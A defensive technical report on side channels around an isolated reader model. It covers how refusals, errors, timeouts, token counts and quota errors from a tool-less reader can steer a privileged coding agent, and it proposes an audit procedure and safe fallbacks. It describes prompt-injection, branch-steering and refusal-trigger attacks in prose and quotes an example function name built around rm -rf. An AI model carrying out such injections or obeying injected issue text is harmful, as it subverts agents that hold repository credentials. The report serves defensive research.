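# Side channels around an isolated reader model: refusals, errors, latency and length

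## The isolated reader and the signals around its answer

A coding agent is a language model that a program runs in a loop, with tools for reading files, running shell commands and changing a code repository. Software projects use such agents to sort incoming bug reports, which GitHub calls issues. Almost anyone with a GitHub account can file one on a public repository, so the agent reads text from strangers while holding credentials for the repository. One remedy is to have a second model, which has no tools, read the report, and to pass only a short answer, such as yes or no, back to the agent. The agent then doesn't see the stranger's sentences, but it may still detect other properties of the call that those sentences affect: whether the second model refuses, whether its output has the wrong form, and how long it runs.

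### Prompt injection and the two-model split

Prompt injection is an attack in which text that a model should only read contains an instruction, and the model obeys it. The attack is possible because programs append outside data *d* to the task *p* and send the model both as one string. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi et al., 2025) gives the example of an agent whose task is to fix the problems in a bug report. The report describes an insecure hash function, then includes an instruction to create a new file, backdoor.py, and the model starts by creating that file. Simon Willison, the software developer who named the attack after SQL injection, writes in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) that nobody knows a reliable way to make a model follow instructions in one category of text while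 safely applying them to another. Detectors help a little, but an attacker can keep rewriting the text until a version gets past them, and Willison considers a 99% detection rate a failing grade in security.

The two-model split does not rely on detecting prompt injections. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes a privileged model, which holds the tools and takes input only from trusted sources, and a quarantined model, which reads the untrusted text, has no tools, and might "go rogue at any moment". An ordinary program, the Controller, sits between them. This report calls the three the privileged agent, the isolated reader and the wrapper, respectively. To summarise an email, the wrapper stores the message as $VAR1, has the isolated reader summarise it, and stores the result as $VAR2. The privileged agent then asks the wrapper to display $VAR2, without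 ever seeing its contents.

Willison allowed one exception, for a reader that sorts text into a fixed set of categories. The wrapper can check that the output is exactly one of those categories and pass it on. In the post's email example, the Controller also tells the privileged model that summarisation has completed. That notice is sent outside $VAR2, and it depends on the reader having finished.

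A hidden value can still cause harm. In the 2025 post, Willison accepts a flaw that Google DeepMind researchers had found in the design. If the privileged agent uses the reader to extract Bob's email address and then sends a document to the result, an instruction in the text can swap in the attacker's address. The agent then sends the document to the attacker, even though it never processed the instruction itself.

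Hidden variables have a more basic problem for a bug-fixing agent, which cannot fix a bug it knows nothing about. Jacob and colleagues therefore let some values through in readable form: integers, floating-point numbers, booleans, and choices from a list the developer has vetted, but no free text. Their reader turns a bug report into a bug category, an estimate of how large the fix will be, and a list of code regions, each with a file number, a start line, an end line and a role. A planner that has seen only this list writes three possible plans in plain language. A judge model that sees the bug report picks one and returns only its index.

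They tested the design on 180 real GitHub issues from the SWE-bench Lite benchmark, using GPT-5.2. An injected request to create an unrelated file succeeded in 98.9% of runs against the ordinary agent and in none against the protected one, but the share of bugs fixed fell from 68.3% to 45.0%. An attack counted as successful only if the extraneous file appeared in the patch, and the threat model excludes attacks that merely mislead the agent. The paper does not discuss refusals, failed parses or timing.

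How much text an isolated reader can safely return is a matter of judgement. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, discusses a suggestion that a reader could turn untrusted documentation into an API description with method names of at most 30 characters. Willison doubts that this is safe, since an attacker might get a name like run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance() through, which a yes-or-no answer would prevent.

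### One question about one issue

Suppose an agent triages issues for a project that contains a parser. For each new issue, the agent needs to know whether it reports a regression in the parser, meaning something that used to work and has stopped working. If the answer is yes, the agent searches the commit history for the change that caused the regression.

The question comes from *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026), which describes a runtime for agents built at Amazon. In that runtime, a small program fetches the page, starts a fresh model with no project files and no network, and reduces the model's reply to yes, no or unclear. Failures, timeouts and any other replies count as unclear. A simpler wrapper, probably closer to what most engineers would write first, accepts only yes or no and doesn't specify what happens when the reader produces neither. Here is one call through the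 simpler wrapper.

1. The author writes the issue and chooses every character of it, including its length, its language, any pasted logs and any instruction aimed at the reader.
2. The wrapper fetches the text, adds the fixed question and sends both to the model provider. *Signals: the size of the input, and an error if the issue is too long for the model.*
3. The provider processes the prompt before the model writes anything. *Signals: a block by a safety filter, and the delay before the first piece of output.*
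4. The reader writes. It may give one word, decline, or reason at length first. *Signals: refusal, output length, running time.*
5. The wrapper checks the output. If it finds neither yes nor no, it may ask again. *Signals: a parse failure, and the number of attempts.*
6. The wrapper returns a result to the privileged agent. On a good run this is the validated answer. *Signals on a bad run: an exception, an error message, an empty result, or silence until a timeout.*
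7. The agent carries on with its work. *Signals: whatever its harness (the program that runs the loop) shows it about elapsed time, tokens used or budget left.*

Only the yes or no in step 6 has passed a check. Everything in italics is an implicit signal. An implicit signal is anything about the reader call, other than the validated answer, that the privileged agent or its control program can observe or act on. Not every system exposes all of these signals. For example, a harness may hide token counts from its model, but a scheduler that stops work when the token budget runs out still acts on them.

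Recent designs treat these signals quite differently. In the agent language of *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), a model call returns either "true" with the parsed value or "false" with the text of the parsing error, and an example program puts that error text into the next prompt. The language labels every value with its origin, so the error text keeps its label, whereas a wrapper in ordinary Python has no such labels. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026), a memory system for agents that also relies on an isolated reader, gives the protected agent the same opaque reply whether a search comes back empty or the reader crashes. It also treats error and status text from tools as untrusted, but its guarantees do not cover timing or termination.

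Eisenach and colleagues acknowledge that their limit on what a page can do holds "provided the call's timing and failures reveal nothing beyond the word". Returning "unclear" when a call fails meets part of that condition, but it doesn't hide the timing, since a call that times out still lasts as long as the timeout. L3M timestamps every record in an agent's log to the millisecond, keeps token counts, and lets a parent agent read the logs of all its descendants. If that access extends to the quarantined reader's logs, the triaging agent could look up both the timing and the reader's raw reply.

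### Covert channels and side channels

Lampson (1973) described an older form of this problem in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*. He asked how a customer could run somebody else's program on private data and be sure that it passed nothing back to the program's owner. Even with files and messages blocked, the program could encode data in the bill for its services, because the owner gets a copy. It could also alternate between heavy computing and heavy disk use, so that another program on the same machine could read the data from changes in the system's speed. Lampson called the bill a legitimate channel and the changes in speed a covert channel, meaning one that was not intended to carry information at all.

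Both have close counterparts in a model call. Providers bill by the token count they report, and latency corresponds to system load. Lampson wanted a program that could pass information only to its caller, but with an isolated reader, the caller's side is the one that needs protection.

Lampson proposed masking, in which the caller fixes in advance everything the confined program can put into such channels, and the operating system enforces this, slowing the program down if necessary. A less demanding option was to accept some leakage and limit its rate. Lampson also doubted that any rigorous method would find every channel in a system of even moderate complexity, and the lists engineers draw up today can likewise miss channels.

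Millen notes in *20 Years of Covert Channel Modeling and Analysis* that "covert channel" later came to include paths through shared storage, which Lampson had kept separate. NIST, the US standards institute, says a *covert channel* needs "two cooperating entities" that pass information against the security policy. In a *covert timing channel*, one entity does this by changing the response time that the other observes. MITRE, a non-profit that catalogues software weaknesses, requires only a path that can carry information in a way the designers did not intend.

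A side channel lets an attacker learn information that a computation leaks through its timing, power use or sound. Usually, nobody sends this information deliberately. NIST's *Side-Channel Attack* entry limits the term to physical cryptographic systems, but work on language models uses it far more loosely.

The issue author fits neither description well. The author may well be sending on purpose, as in a covert channel, but the privileged agent has not agreed on a code and is not cooperating. The reader transmits unintentionally, which is more like a side channel. MITRE's wording covers this case, unlike NIST's.

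### Out to an observer, in to the agent

Most published attacks on language model services carry secret information out to someone who should not have it. In *Whisper Leak*, McDonald and Bar Or (2025) recorded the sizes and timing of encrypted packets while 28 models streamed their replies. They trained classifiers to pick out questions about the legality of money laundering from thousands of unrelated ones. For 17 of the models, the classifiers scored above 98% on a measure that combines precision and recall. The attacker in that study only observes traffic, from an internet provider or a café's wireless network. *Mirage* (2026) defends against active attackers, who submit guesses to a shared service and learn from the response time how much of a guess matches text the service has already processed.

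Refusals and errors also leak information outward. In *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (2026), models asked to repeat a list of short strings either left out the one that overlapped with a secret or refused the whole list. Either reaction revealed the overlap. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that an exception that occurs only when a secret meets some condition reveals one bit per run. Garby and colleagues add that a retry loop outside the security monitor lets an attacker repeat the process until they have recovered the whole secret.

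The concern with an isolated reader runs the other way.

| | Secret going out | Influence coming in |
|---|---|---|
| Sender | A model service or agent, usually unwittingly | The issue's author, by way of the reader |
| Receiver | The attacker | The privileged agent or its control program |
| What the attacker controls | Sometimes only a place to listen, sometimes probe prompts | The whole text of the issue, and often how many issues there are |
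| What goes wrong | Somebody learns private data | The agent does something its user did not intend |

Eisenach and colleagues treat the two as mirror images. For the outward case they take a private agent that can reach a network only by writing to a separate research agent. Let *S* be the private source code, *M* the messages the private agent sends, *E* everything the research agent emits, and *Z* the public inputs. If *E* depends on *S* only through *M*, and padding fixes the total size of *M* at *k* bytes, then

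*I*(*S*; *E* | *Z*) ≤ *I*(*S*; *M* | *Z*) ≤ *H*(*M* | *Z*) ≤ 8*k* bits.

However much the research agent sends, what leaves can reveal no more about the source than the messages could hold. The timing and number of messages must count towards *M*, or the system must prevent them from acting as signals. The three-word menu similarly limits inward influence. Under the condition on timing and failures, a page can affect only which of three outcomes occurs in each call, which limits its influence to log₂ 3, or about 1.6, bits per call.

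For an attacker, the inward direction is easier in some ways. A listener on a network has to separate a signal from noise, whereas a refusal may reach the privileged agent as a clean status code. Encryption makes no difference to an inward attack. Millen describes the classic covert channel as hard work because the attacker had to plant a program inside the system and run a cooperating receiver beside it. An attacker who writes an issue needs to do neither, but does need an agent that reacts to the signal in some useful way. The outward studies show that length, timing and refusals vary with the text, but they give no evidence that an agent would react this way.

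The threat is limited and easy to overstate. A false issue can persuade an honest reader to answer yes, and a hijacked reader can answer yes to anything. The agent then wastes an afternoon of computing on a regression that never happened. This influence comes through the validated answer itself, so hiding every implicit signal would not prevent it. Eisenach and colleagues note that a wrong no is also an error.

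A timeout also can't carry instructions to the agent, because it contains no sentence, file name or command. An error message that quotes the reader's output can contain all of these, but then the wrapper has let untrusted text through and the problem is ordinary prompt injection. A bare timeout can only trigger a reaction that was already available to the agent or set up by its developer, a kind of influence known as branch steering. Sometimes that reaction is harmless, such as leaving the issue for a human. But if the agent reacts to the missing answer by reading the issue itself, the injected instruction reaches the one model that has the tools.

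## Listing the signals and tracing what the agent does next

Whether a timeout does harm depends on the code that handles it. An engineer auditing an isolated reader therefore has to trace each signal from the text of the issue to the last thing the agent or its harness does in response. Most of this work is reading code: the provider's response format, the exceptions its client library can raise, the wrapper, and everything that runs after the wrapper returns.

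### The audit procedure

1. List everything the privileged side can reach after one call to the reader. Include every field of the provider's response, every exception, every log line, every counter (attempts, tokens, remaining budget) and every clock, even if no code uses it today.
2. Next to each entry, write who can read it.
3. Write how the issue's author could change it, assuming that they know the code. On a public repository they often do, because the workflow files that start the agent are public too.
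4. Write what ought to happen for each value the entry can take. Do this before looking at how the code handles it.
5. Trace what actually happens. Don't stop at the wrapper's return statement, but follow the value until something acts on it or drops it.
6. Mark every outcome that gives the agent more access to the issue, more authority or fewer checks than a valid answer would. Fix those first.

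Step 4 comes before step 5 because a missing check leaves nothing in the code to find. Weng, Wang and colleagues (2026) designed their study of 40 open-source agent systems, *When Code Becomes an LLM Call*, around this problem. They found 496 places where a program calls a model and acts on the reply. One AI agent read a description of each call's job, without seeing the code, and worked out which checks the call needed. Another listed the checks that the code made. Human reviewers then reviewed the results. 82% of the call sites had checks both before and after the call, but only 5.3% had all the checks they needed.

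Tracing can also go wrong. In Skyvern, a browser agent from the same study, the policy engine denied a forbidden click in every test run, but the code that carries out clicks never read the decision. An auditor who stopped at the policy engine would have marked that path as safe.

### Three receivers

A signal can enter the context of the agent's model as text, reach control code that branches on it, or end up in a log that a person or a later job reads.

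If the wrapper sends the agent the message "reader failed: timeout after 60 seconds", the agent's model, rather than any code, determines what the agent does next. An auditor can therefore only find out by testing, and a new model version may react differently.

Control code is easier to audit because its reactions are written down, but an attacker can read them too. Much of what models produce ends up in such code. Weng and colleagues split the replies at the call sites they studied into 917 separate outputs and found that 48% reached control flow or were executed as code. Of those, 73% never reached a person. The figures cover replies, not error codes, though code that branches on a reply also has to do something when the reply is missing.

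Signals in logs take longer to have an effect. A maintainer who sees forty reader failures in a morning may switch the reader off until somebody has time to investigate. A nightly job may collect the failed issues and give them to another agent for diagnosis, with the raw text attached. Where one agent can read another's logs, as in L3M, a log entry may also end up back in a model's context.

The list should name each signal's receiver exactly, because a system can be secure against one observer but not another. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, proves this for secrets that leak outward. In one example, a user approves the exact text of an email reply, and an injected instruction tries to send private data instead. The monitor allows the injected message only if the private data is identical to the approved reply. An attacker who sees only the messages receives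 the same reply either way. An attacker who also sees when each step happens can learn whether the two texts match, because the injected copy goes out a step early. Dongol also defines an even stronger observer, who can see refused requests through an error message or a log. The proofs don't cover hijacking, but an audit of inward influence should be equally precise about who can see each signal.

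### The list for the parser question

The table applies the procedure to the simpler yes-or-no wrapper from the previous section. That wrapper doesn't specify how to handle failures, so the last column gives reactions that a developer might have written or an agent might improvise.

| Signal | Who can read it | How the issue's author can change it | What may happen next |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stop reason (the provider's code for why the model stopped) | Wrapper; the agent's model if the wrapper passes on the whole response | Include text that the model declines or a filter blocks, or provoke a reply that hits the length limit | The wrapper retries or switches to another model |
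| Refusal text | Wrapper and log; the agent's model if it gets the raw reply | Choose the subject that the refusal mentions | The agent reads a sentence that the issue helped to shape |
| Validation error | Wrapper and log; the agent's model if the exception reaches it | Get the reader to write something other than yes or no | The agent opens the issue to see what went wrong |
| Attempt count | Wrapper and log | Make some or all of the attempts fail | After the last attempt, the wrapper uses its default |
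| Token usage | Wrapper, billing job, budget scheduler; sometimes the agent's model | Write a long issue or provoke long reasoning | The scheduler ends the run with other issues unread |
| Cached-token count (input for which the provider reused stored computation) | Wrapper and billing records | Repeat the text of an earlier issue | Usually nothing, unless code uses it to spot duplicates |
| Elapsed time | Anything with a clock, including an agent with a shell | Write a long issue or one that is slow to reason about | A timeout fires, or the agent drops the check to save time |
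| Quota or rate-limit error | Wrapper; the agent's harness if they share an account | File many issues, or very long ones | Checks on unrelated issues fail as well |
| Missing result | All three receivers | Cause any of the failures above | Code treats the gap as "no", or the agent reads the issue itself |

Several of the listed signals may turn out to be harmless. For example, a cached-token count that appears only on an invoice can't affect what the agent does. It still belongs on the list because a developer may later write code that uses it.

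Elapsed time is the hardest signal to take away from an agent with a shell, because it can run the `date` command before and after the call. PerMIT, the memory system from the previous section, puts clock readings from tools in the untrusted store, as it does with all other tool output, so the protected agent never sees them. This rule would be awkward for a coding agent, which usually needs to see what its commands print.

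### Quota errors

A quota error is easy to miss because it can appear in a different call from the one that caused it. Jiang and colleagues found such a case in their own design, PerMIT. Their proofs treat its store of untrusted content as unlimited, but a real store fills up. The store holds whatever the agent's tools bring in from outside, so an attacker can influence how much goes into it. An error telling the protected agent that the store was full would reveal a volume that the attacker had chosen. PerMIT gives identical replies to crashes and empty searches, which are meant to hide the amount of untrusted memory as well as its content, and the quota error would undo that protection. Jiang and colleagues therefore require a deployment to delete untrusted entries silently when space runs out, although something useful may then disappear without the agent noticing.

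When a user reviews a long set of retrieved items, the agent learns only whether the user accepted the whole set. This hides the number of pages, which one decision per page would reveal. The user therefore can't reject a poisoned item without losing the rest of the batch.

For the triage agent, the likely equivalent is a rate limit. If the reader and the privileged agent share a provider account, somebody who files fifty very long issues can use up the account's allowance and cause errors in calls unrelated to those issues. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Detour Is the Danger*, describe a version in which an attacker controls another application under the same quota and exhausts that quota. This blocks the service that scans files for sensitive content, while the upload service keeps working.

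### Branch steering

A bare status code can only trigger a reaction that already exists. Often that reaction is code that runs if the reader fails, and the issue's author can influence whether that code runs.

Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues named this kind of attack *branch steering* in January 2026. They study computer-use agents, which operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. In their design, a trusted planner writes the complete program before any model looks at the screen. A quarantined vision model then describes the screen, and another isolated call uses that description to answer a question such as "is a cookie banner visible?" The true-or-false answer selects a branch of the program.

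This design guarantees *control-flow integrity*, which means only actions in the plan can run, in the order and under the conditions the planner set. It does not guarantee *data-flow security*, which would also prevent untrusted data from setting the arguments of those actions or the values that determine which branch runs. In a branch steering attack, an attacker manipulates what the reader observes so that the agent takes a valid branch of its plan that suits the attacker.

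The main example uses cookie banners. Nearly every plan that involves a website includes a step to find and dismiss the cookie popup. In the test, the vision model returned the coordinates of a fake popup placed inside an advertisement, and the agent clicked on it and landed on a page the attacker chose. Checking the vision model's output against the page's underlying structure stopped the attack for simple image advertisements. It failed for advertisements that can contain their own HTML, because these can replace the label that marks them as advertising.

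Foerster and colleagues argue that such attacks get harder as they require more false observations and a better guess at the plan. The cookie step requires only one false observation and is the same for almost every task. The plans in their study contained 39.7 branches on average, compared with 3.7 for agents with ordinary text-based tools, and about half of the steps were fallbacks that a given run never used. Error handling in a coding agent is similar because a developer wrote it in advance, the same handler serves every issue, and most test runs never reach it.

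In *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026) measured how often the attacks work using STEER-Bench, a benchmark of 101 tasks in nine domains, including bank transfers, warehouse logistics and changes to a patient's dose. Attacks succeeded in 94.4% of cases against an ordinary agent and in 89.5% against one with a separate planner and reader, so the separation made little difference to this kind of attack. Both figures come from the 74 of the 199 attack cases that generic computer-use agents can run.

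Their defence, COBRA, limits what each branch can do. Before the agent sees any untrusted page, the planner specifies which sites each branch may contact, which tools it may call and which values it may send. Ordinary programs then check each outgoing web request and tool call against the current branch's limits. An attacker may still push the agent into a branch, but the agent can only do there what the planner allowed. COBRA blocked all 199 attacks and kept 97% of the split agent's performance on tasks without an attack. It wrongly blocked four of 138 harmless runs.

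The 97% figure compares COBRA with an agent that also planned blind, so it leaves out the performance lost to blind planning. On a separate set of 361 desktop tasks, COBRA with Sonnet-5 in both roles completed 38.8%, while an ordinary Sonnet-5 agent completed 51.0%. The protection also depends on how precise the constraints are. In a test with web agents, limiting the agent to approved sites let 14 of 19 attacks through, because the forbidden action was on an approved site. In one of these, the user had asked for a comment on a GitLab issue, and the injected text tried to add a deploy key, which gives access to a repository. A list of permitted operations for each site stopped all 19. A rule that lets a coding agent contact only GitHub would probably have the same weakness.

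These results don't carry over directly to status signals. The agents in STEER-Bench operate screens, and their reader is UI-TARS-1.5-7B, a small model that may be easier to mislead than the one a software team would choose. The attacks work mainly through values that end up in an action, such as an amount, a destination or a tool argument, and none of the nine test suites targets refusals, timeouts or failed parses. An issue's author might be able to steer a coding agent in the same way through a failed call, but this is an inference. COBRA's plans can branch on failure. When a tool call returns an error, the plan may continue through the screen instead. The constraints still apply on that route, so it is a reasonable pattern for a fallback.

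Ma and colleagues address the question more directly because they tested what agents do after a tool fails. Each task included a protection, such as backing up a file before changing it, scanning a document before uploading it or checking access before querying a database. The researchers made some tools fail without adding any malicious text. When they targeted the protective tool, the agent lost the protection in 41 of 249 runs, compared with 9 of 247 when the faults were random. Part of that gap arose because the two kinds of fault reached the agent at different rates. The agent still finished its task in 39 of the 50 runs that lost the protection, so a dashboard that tracks only completed tasks would not have shown the problem in those cases.

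Changing the error message hardly helped. In a follow-up with four models, agents lost the protection in 30% to 34% of runs whether the tool reported a failure, an incomplete result or an unknown status (43 of 143, 44 of 143 and 48 of 142). Repeated failures increased the risk for some models. DeepSeek V4 Pro lost the protection in 7 of 36 runs after a single permitted failure and in 20 of 36 when up to three were possible, but Qwen Plus showed no such increase. A wrapper that reports each failed attempt to the agent may therefore be riskier than one that reports a single result at the end.

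The researchers caused the failures deliberately, so the study shows how agents react to a failure but not that the text of an issue can cause one. The agents also skipped protections in a third of the runs without a failure. Of the seven models tested, some are older, such as GPT-4o mini, and one, DeepSeek Flash, kept the protection in all 36 targeted runs of the first experiment.

### Unsafe fallbacks and safer ones

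A fallback is what the system does when the reader gives no valid answer. It is unsafe if it relaxes a protection.

Handing the raw issue to the privileged agent is the worst choice, since it removes the isolation just when the text has caused odd behavior. A developer might do this expecting the agent's stronger model to sort the problem out. An attacker then needs an issue with two parts, one that makes the reader fail and one that tells the agent what to do. The agent can end up reading the raw issue even if nobody wrote such a fallback, because when it is told that the reader failed on issue 412, it may simply fetch issue 412 with its GitHub tool. The safe version returns "unclear", leaves the issue to a person, and denies the agent any tool that could read the issue's text. The drawback is that a genuine bug report waits until somebody looks at it.

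Designers of robot controllers face a similar choice. *AuthGuard-R* (2026) describes a system that checks a language model's commands before a robot carries them out. If the checker fails, the system rejects ordinary commands, even though the robot will sometimes stop working as a result. The paper warns against executing the model's raw command merely because the checker has crashed. A few emergency actions, such as stopping or asking a person for help, can be approved in advance. For an issue-triage agent, the only pre-approved action might be adding a "needs human review" label.

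Switching to a weaker reader does less damage. The replacement still has no tools and can still return only yes or no, so the attacker gains at most a wrong answer. But the issue's author can now influence which model judges the text. *When Efficiency Backfires* (2026) studies a related arrangement called a cascade, in which a weak model handles some queries and a decision module passes the others to a stronger one. The attack adds a string of text that makes the weak model answer every query itself. It cut accuracy by up to 52.2% even after the researchers replaced the weak model with one that the attack had not been built for. A fallback switches from a strong model to a weak one, but it also leaves a weaker model judging the hostile text. It is safer to keep a second reader that has passed the same tests as the first, and to return "unclear" if both fail. That means paying for a second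 capable model and retesting it with every update.

Suppose the reader screens pull requests before the agent runs their tests with its own credentials. If the agent runs the tests even when the reader times out, the author of a pull request can bypass the screening by causing a timeout. The agent can safely hold the pull request instead, or run the tests in a container without credentials or network access, though some tests will not work there.

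Ma and colleagues built this kind of substitution into a defence called ARGUS. It attaches the requirement to the risky action, so the agent may use any scanner but can't send a file without a valid scan of its current contents. They compared a version that only blocks unsafe actions with one that also tells the agent what is missing and how to obtain it. Neither version lost a protection in 576 scheduled runs, while the agents without a defence did so 97 times. Guidance helped the agents complete more tasks when the protective tool failed. GPT-4o mini completed 25.7% of its tasks with blocking alone and 63.6% with guidance, while DeepSeek Flash went from 77.8% to 100%. It matters that the guidance came from trusted code, because advice from the failed reader could contain the attacker's text.

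Programmers often make "safe" the default without meaning to. Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, has an optional check in which a model judges whether a proposed tool call follows a security policy. Weng and colleagues found that the check returns "allow" if the reply is empty or doesn't parse, or if the request fails. Two later safeguards would block the call if the check reported an error, but it reports an approval instead. STORM, a research-writing system, asks a model whether a topic is appropriate and rejects it only if the reply starts with "No", so a refusal to answer counts as approval.

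In Python, a failed call that returns `None` can count as a "no" even without error handling, because an `if` statement treats `None` as false. This does little harm if the question is "does this issue report a parser regression?", since the agent only skips a search, but if the question is "does this issue look malicious?", the agent treats the issue as harmless.

Weng and colleagues counted 146 gaps of this sort across 30 of their 40 systems, though few appeared to matter for an attack. In 23 of them, a bad value could lead to a harmful effect, but rejecting invalid replies would have narrowed the attack in only one case and stopped it in none. Their screening excluded faults that need a non-default setting and faults in parsing or retry code that all outputs share, so it may undercount the cases that concern an isolated reader. The repair takes little work in any case. The wrapper should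 return "unclear" as a separate value, and each caller should have to handle it explicitly, although this will leave a larger number of harmless issues waiting for review.

Any of these safe fallbacks gives an attacker some control over how much work goes undone. An attacker who files two hundred issues that the reader refuses can fill the maintainers' review queue and bury the genuine reports. Limiting each account's unresolved issues in the queue makes this harder, but the attacker can create new accounts for free.

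## Refusals that an issue's author can trigger

An attacker needs text that the reader refuses in order to fill a review queue with refused issues or trigger an unsafe fallback. The model may decline in ordinary prose, or the refusal may come from a safety classifier, a separate program that the provider runs on the prompt and the reply. The classifier can stop a call before the first word or partway through the answer. Both kinds of refusal depend on the issue's text, so the issue's author has some control over them.

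### How refusals reach the wrapper

A wrapper often asks for output that fits a schema, a machine-readable description of the answer's required format. The provider enforces the schema by limiting which tokens the model can choose. But Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, a guide to the Claude models, states that a refusal message takes precedence over the schema, and OpenAI's *Structured Outputs* warns that a refusal may not follow it. Anthropic's *Refusals and fallback* and Google's *Safety and content filters* describe what the wrapper receives instead.

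| Provider | How a refusal appears | What is left of the answer |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Stop reason `refusal`, with a policy category and a one-sentence explanation | Nothing, or a fragment |
| OpenAI | A `refusal` field with the model's own words, or the finish reason `content_filter` | No valid answer, or JSON that breaks off partway |
| Google | A block reason for the prompt, or a finish reason such as `SAFETY` | An empty content field |

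Anthropic returns a refusal as a successful response, with HTTP status code 200, so code that only catches errors will miss it. If the content list is empty, a wrapper that reads its first item crashes with an index error, and the log records a bug instead of a refusal. *Handle streaming refusals* adds that a refused request in a batch job counts as succeeded. In Anthropic's Managed Agents service, a refused turn can carry `end_turn`, the stop reason for normal completion.

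When Claude itself declines, the API returns ordinary text. The wrapper detects the refusal only because "I can't help with that" is neither yes nor no, and it records a parse failure.

A strict schema can hide a refusal. In a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, *All "refusal" keys are null, even if refusal is true*, a developer using an older version of OpenAI's Python library found the `refusal` field empty and the model's apology in one of the schema's text fields. When the schema allowed only a whole number, the model returned a word count of 0. This is a single report, and current models may behave differently. A schema that allows only yes and no has the same problem, because a model that would otherwise refuse has to return one of them. Adding "unclear" to the schema gives it another option.

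Google's blocked responses can also include a probability score and a severity score for each of four harm categories, and the documentation's examples show most of these scores to about eight digits. An issue's author can influence these numbers, so the wrapper shouldn't pass them on. The configurable filters are off by default for recent Gemini models, but the filters for child sexual abuse material and some personal information always apply.

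Anthropic can retry a refused request on another Claude model within the same call. The wrapper then gets a valid yes or no, but the response still names the model that answered and lists the declined attempt. In a streamed reply, the delay before the first byte includes that attempt. For about an hour afterwards, Anthropic may send requests in the same conversation straight to the second model. According to OpenAI's *Safety checks*, the company may hold back a streamed reply while it runs further checks on a user who may be breaking its rules. If the checks fail, no tokens arrive.

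### The test string

In September 2025, Anthropic's *Handle streaming refusals* included a long, fixed string that made Claude refuse. A refusal in the middle of a reply could leave an application with half a sentence and, at that time, no refusal message. This was awkward to test, and the string let developers trigger it without writing a prompt that broke Anthropic's rules. *The Refusal String Attack* (2026) compares the string to the EICAR file, a harmless file that antivirus programs deliberately flag so that people can check their scanner works.

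The string also worked when it came from somebody else. Frichette, in *[Deprecated] Claude Magic String Denial of Service*, lists the routes into a prompt, including tickets, wiki pages, logs and stack traces. A bug report is a ticket and often contains a pasted log or stack trace. The blogger Aphyr tested the string on web pages and found that Claude ended the chat only when the string was inside a `code` tag. Aphyr then added it to every page of the blog in response to a flood of LLM spam. When a commenter asked whether the string would also stop Claude from working on a code repository, Aphyr thought it would.

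The effect could outlast a single call because an application that holds a conversation usually resends the whole history with each new message. Once the string was in that history, every later call failed until somebody removed the message or cleared the history. *The Refusal String Attack*, a first-person account, describes an agent with a similar problem, whose session ended every time its scheduled job fetched a Wikipedia talk page where somebody had posted the string. An isolated reader that starts afresh for each issue would lose only one answer, but a reader that takes twenty issues in one prompt to save money would lose all twenty.

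In *Hard-stopping AI agent pipelines with prompt-level kill switches*, Olejnik describes how a document containing the string could stop its own review. In the example, a model reads the document and decides which checks to run on it. If the call ends before the model decides, none of the checks run, and the record can look like a normal completion. Olejnik recommends marking such a document "assessment incomplete" and trying again with a filter that doesn't use a language model.

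Frichette also cites a piece of malware as a real use of the technique, and reports that Anthropic had patched the problem as of May 2026. Anthropic's current guide to streaming refusals no longer includes the string. Even before the patch, a wrapper could have removed the string from its input. The patch doesn't address ordinary text about a forbidden subject, which is much harder to filter out.

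### Ordinary text that causes refusals

In June 2026, text of this kind turned up in password- and key-stealing malware in packages on PyPI, the main public index of Python software. The malware belonged to the Hades wave of the Shai-Hulud campaign. Endor Labs' *Shai-Hulud Hades wave hits six PyPI bioinformatics packages* describes a JavaScript file of about 5.4 megabytes whose first 99 lines are a comment. The comment is a fake classified briefing containing requests for step-by-step instructions for biological weapons and nuclear devices. The program itself is on line 101. The comment has no effect when the file runs, but a language model analysing the file from the top reads it before reaching the program.

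SC Media's *Mini Shai-Hulud Hades variant affects 23 PyPI package versions* reports that researchers at the security company Socket think the comment was probably there to make the model refuse. The OSV vulnerability-database record *Malicious code in pyphetools (PyPI)* (2026) gives the same explanation. Schneier's *Embedding Forbidden Text in Spyware to Discourage AI Analysis* (2026) quotes an analysis that adds confusion and premature classification as possible effects, and notes that conventional detection, such as pattern matching and behavioral rules, still works. The security company ESET calls this type of comment GuardBreaker.

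These reports show that attackers think the trick is worth trying, but they don't measure how often a current model refuses to analyse the file. An issue's author could easily copy the text.

Harmless text can also cause refusals. Anthropic warns that legitimate security work can trigger its `cyber` category, so a genuine vulnerability report with exploit code attached is more likely than most issues to cause a refusal, and it may be the one that maintainers most need to see. A refusal is therefore weak evidence of an attack. Anthropic's classifiers also block requests to write out the model's internal reasoning. A schema with a field for step-by-step reasoning can cause such a refusal without any attacker, and an issue that asks the reader model to print its private notes might cause one too.

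The most detailed measurements come from *Machine Against the RAG* (Shafran, Schuster and Shmatikov, 2024) and cover models that are now old. The paper tests an attack on systems that retrieve the five documents most similar to a question and give them to a model to answer from. The attacker adds one "blocker" document to the collection, intended to stop the system from answering one particular question. The blocker opens with that question, which was enough to get it retrieved more than 97% of the time. A search program chooses the next 50 tokens, using only the system's replies. It starts with 50 exclamation marks, tries random replacements for one token at a time, and keeps whichever version moves the reply closest to a target refusal.

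The researchers tested this on six open models, with two datasets, two retrieval models and three target refusals. Depending on the combination, the blockers stopped between 28% and 73% of the answers the system would otherwise have given. A plain instruction to ignore the other documents and refuse sometimes worked better, but this depended on the wording of the refusal. In one setting with Llama-2-7b, the instruction stopped 90% of answers when the requested reply was "I don't know", but only 34% when the model had to say it was declining because the answer would be false or misleading.

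Blockers made for one of the six models stopped at most 19% of answers from another. The researchers built blockers directly against three larger commercial models, using ten questions for each, and stopped three answers from GPT-4o mini, one from GPT-4o and three from Gemini 1.5 Flash. Models with higher safety scores tended to be more vulnerable. Even without an attack, Gemini 1.5 Pro refused to say where *Sex and the City* takes place because the question triggered a sexual content filter.

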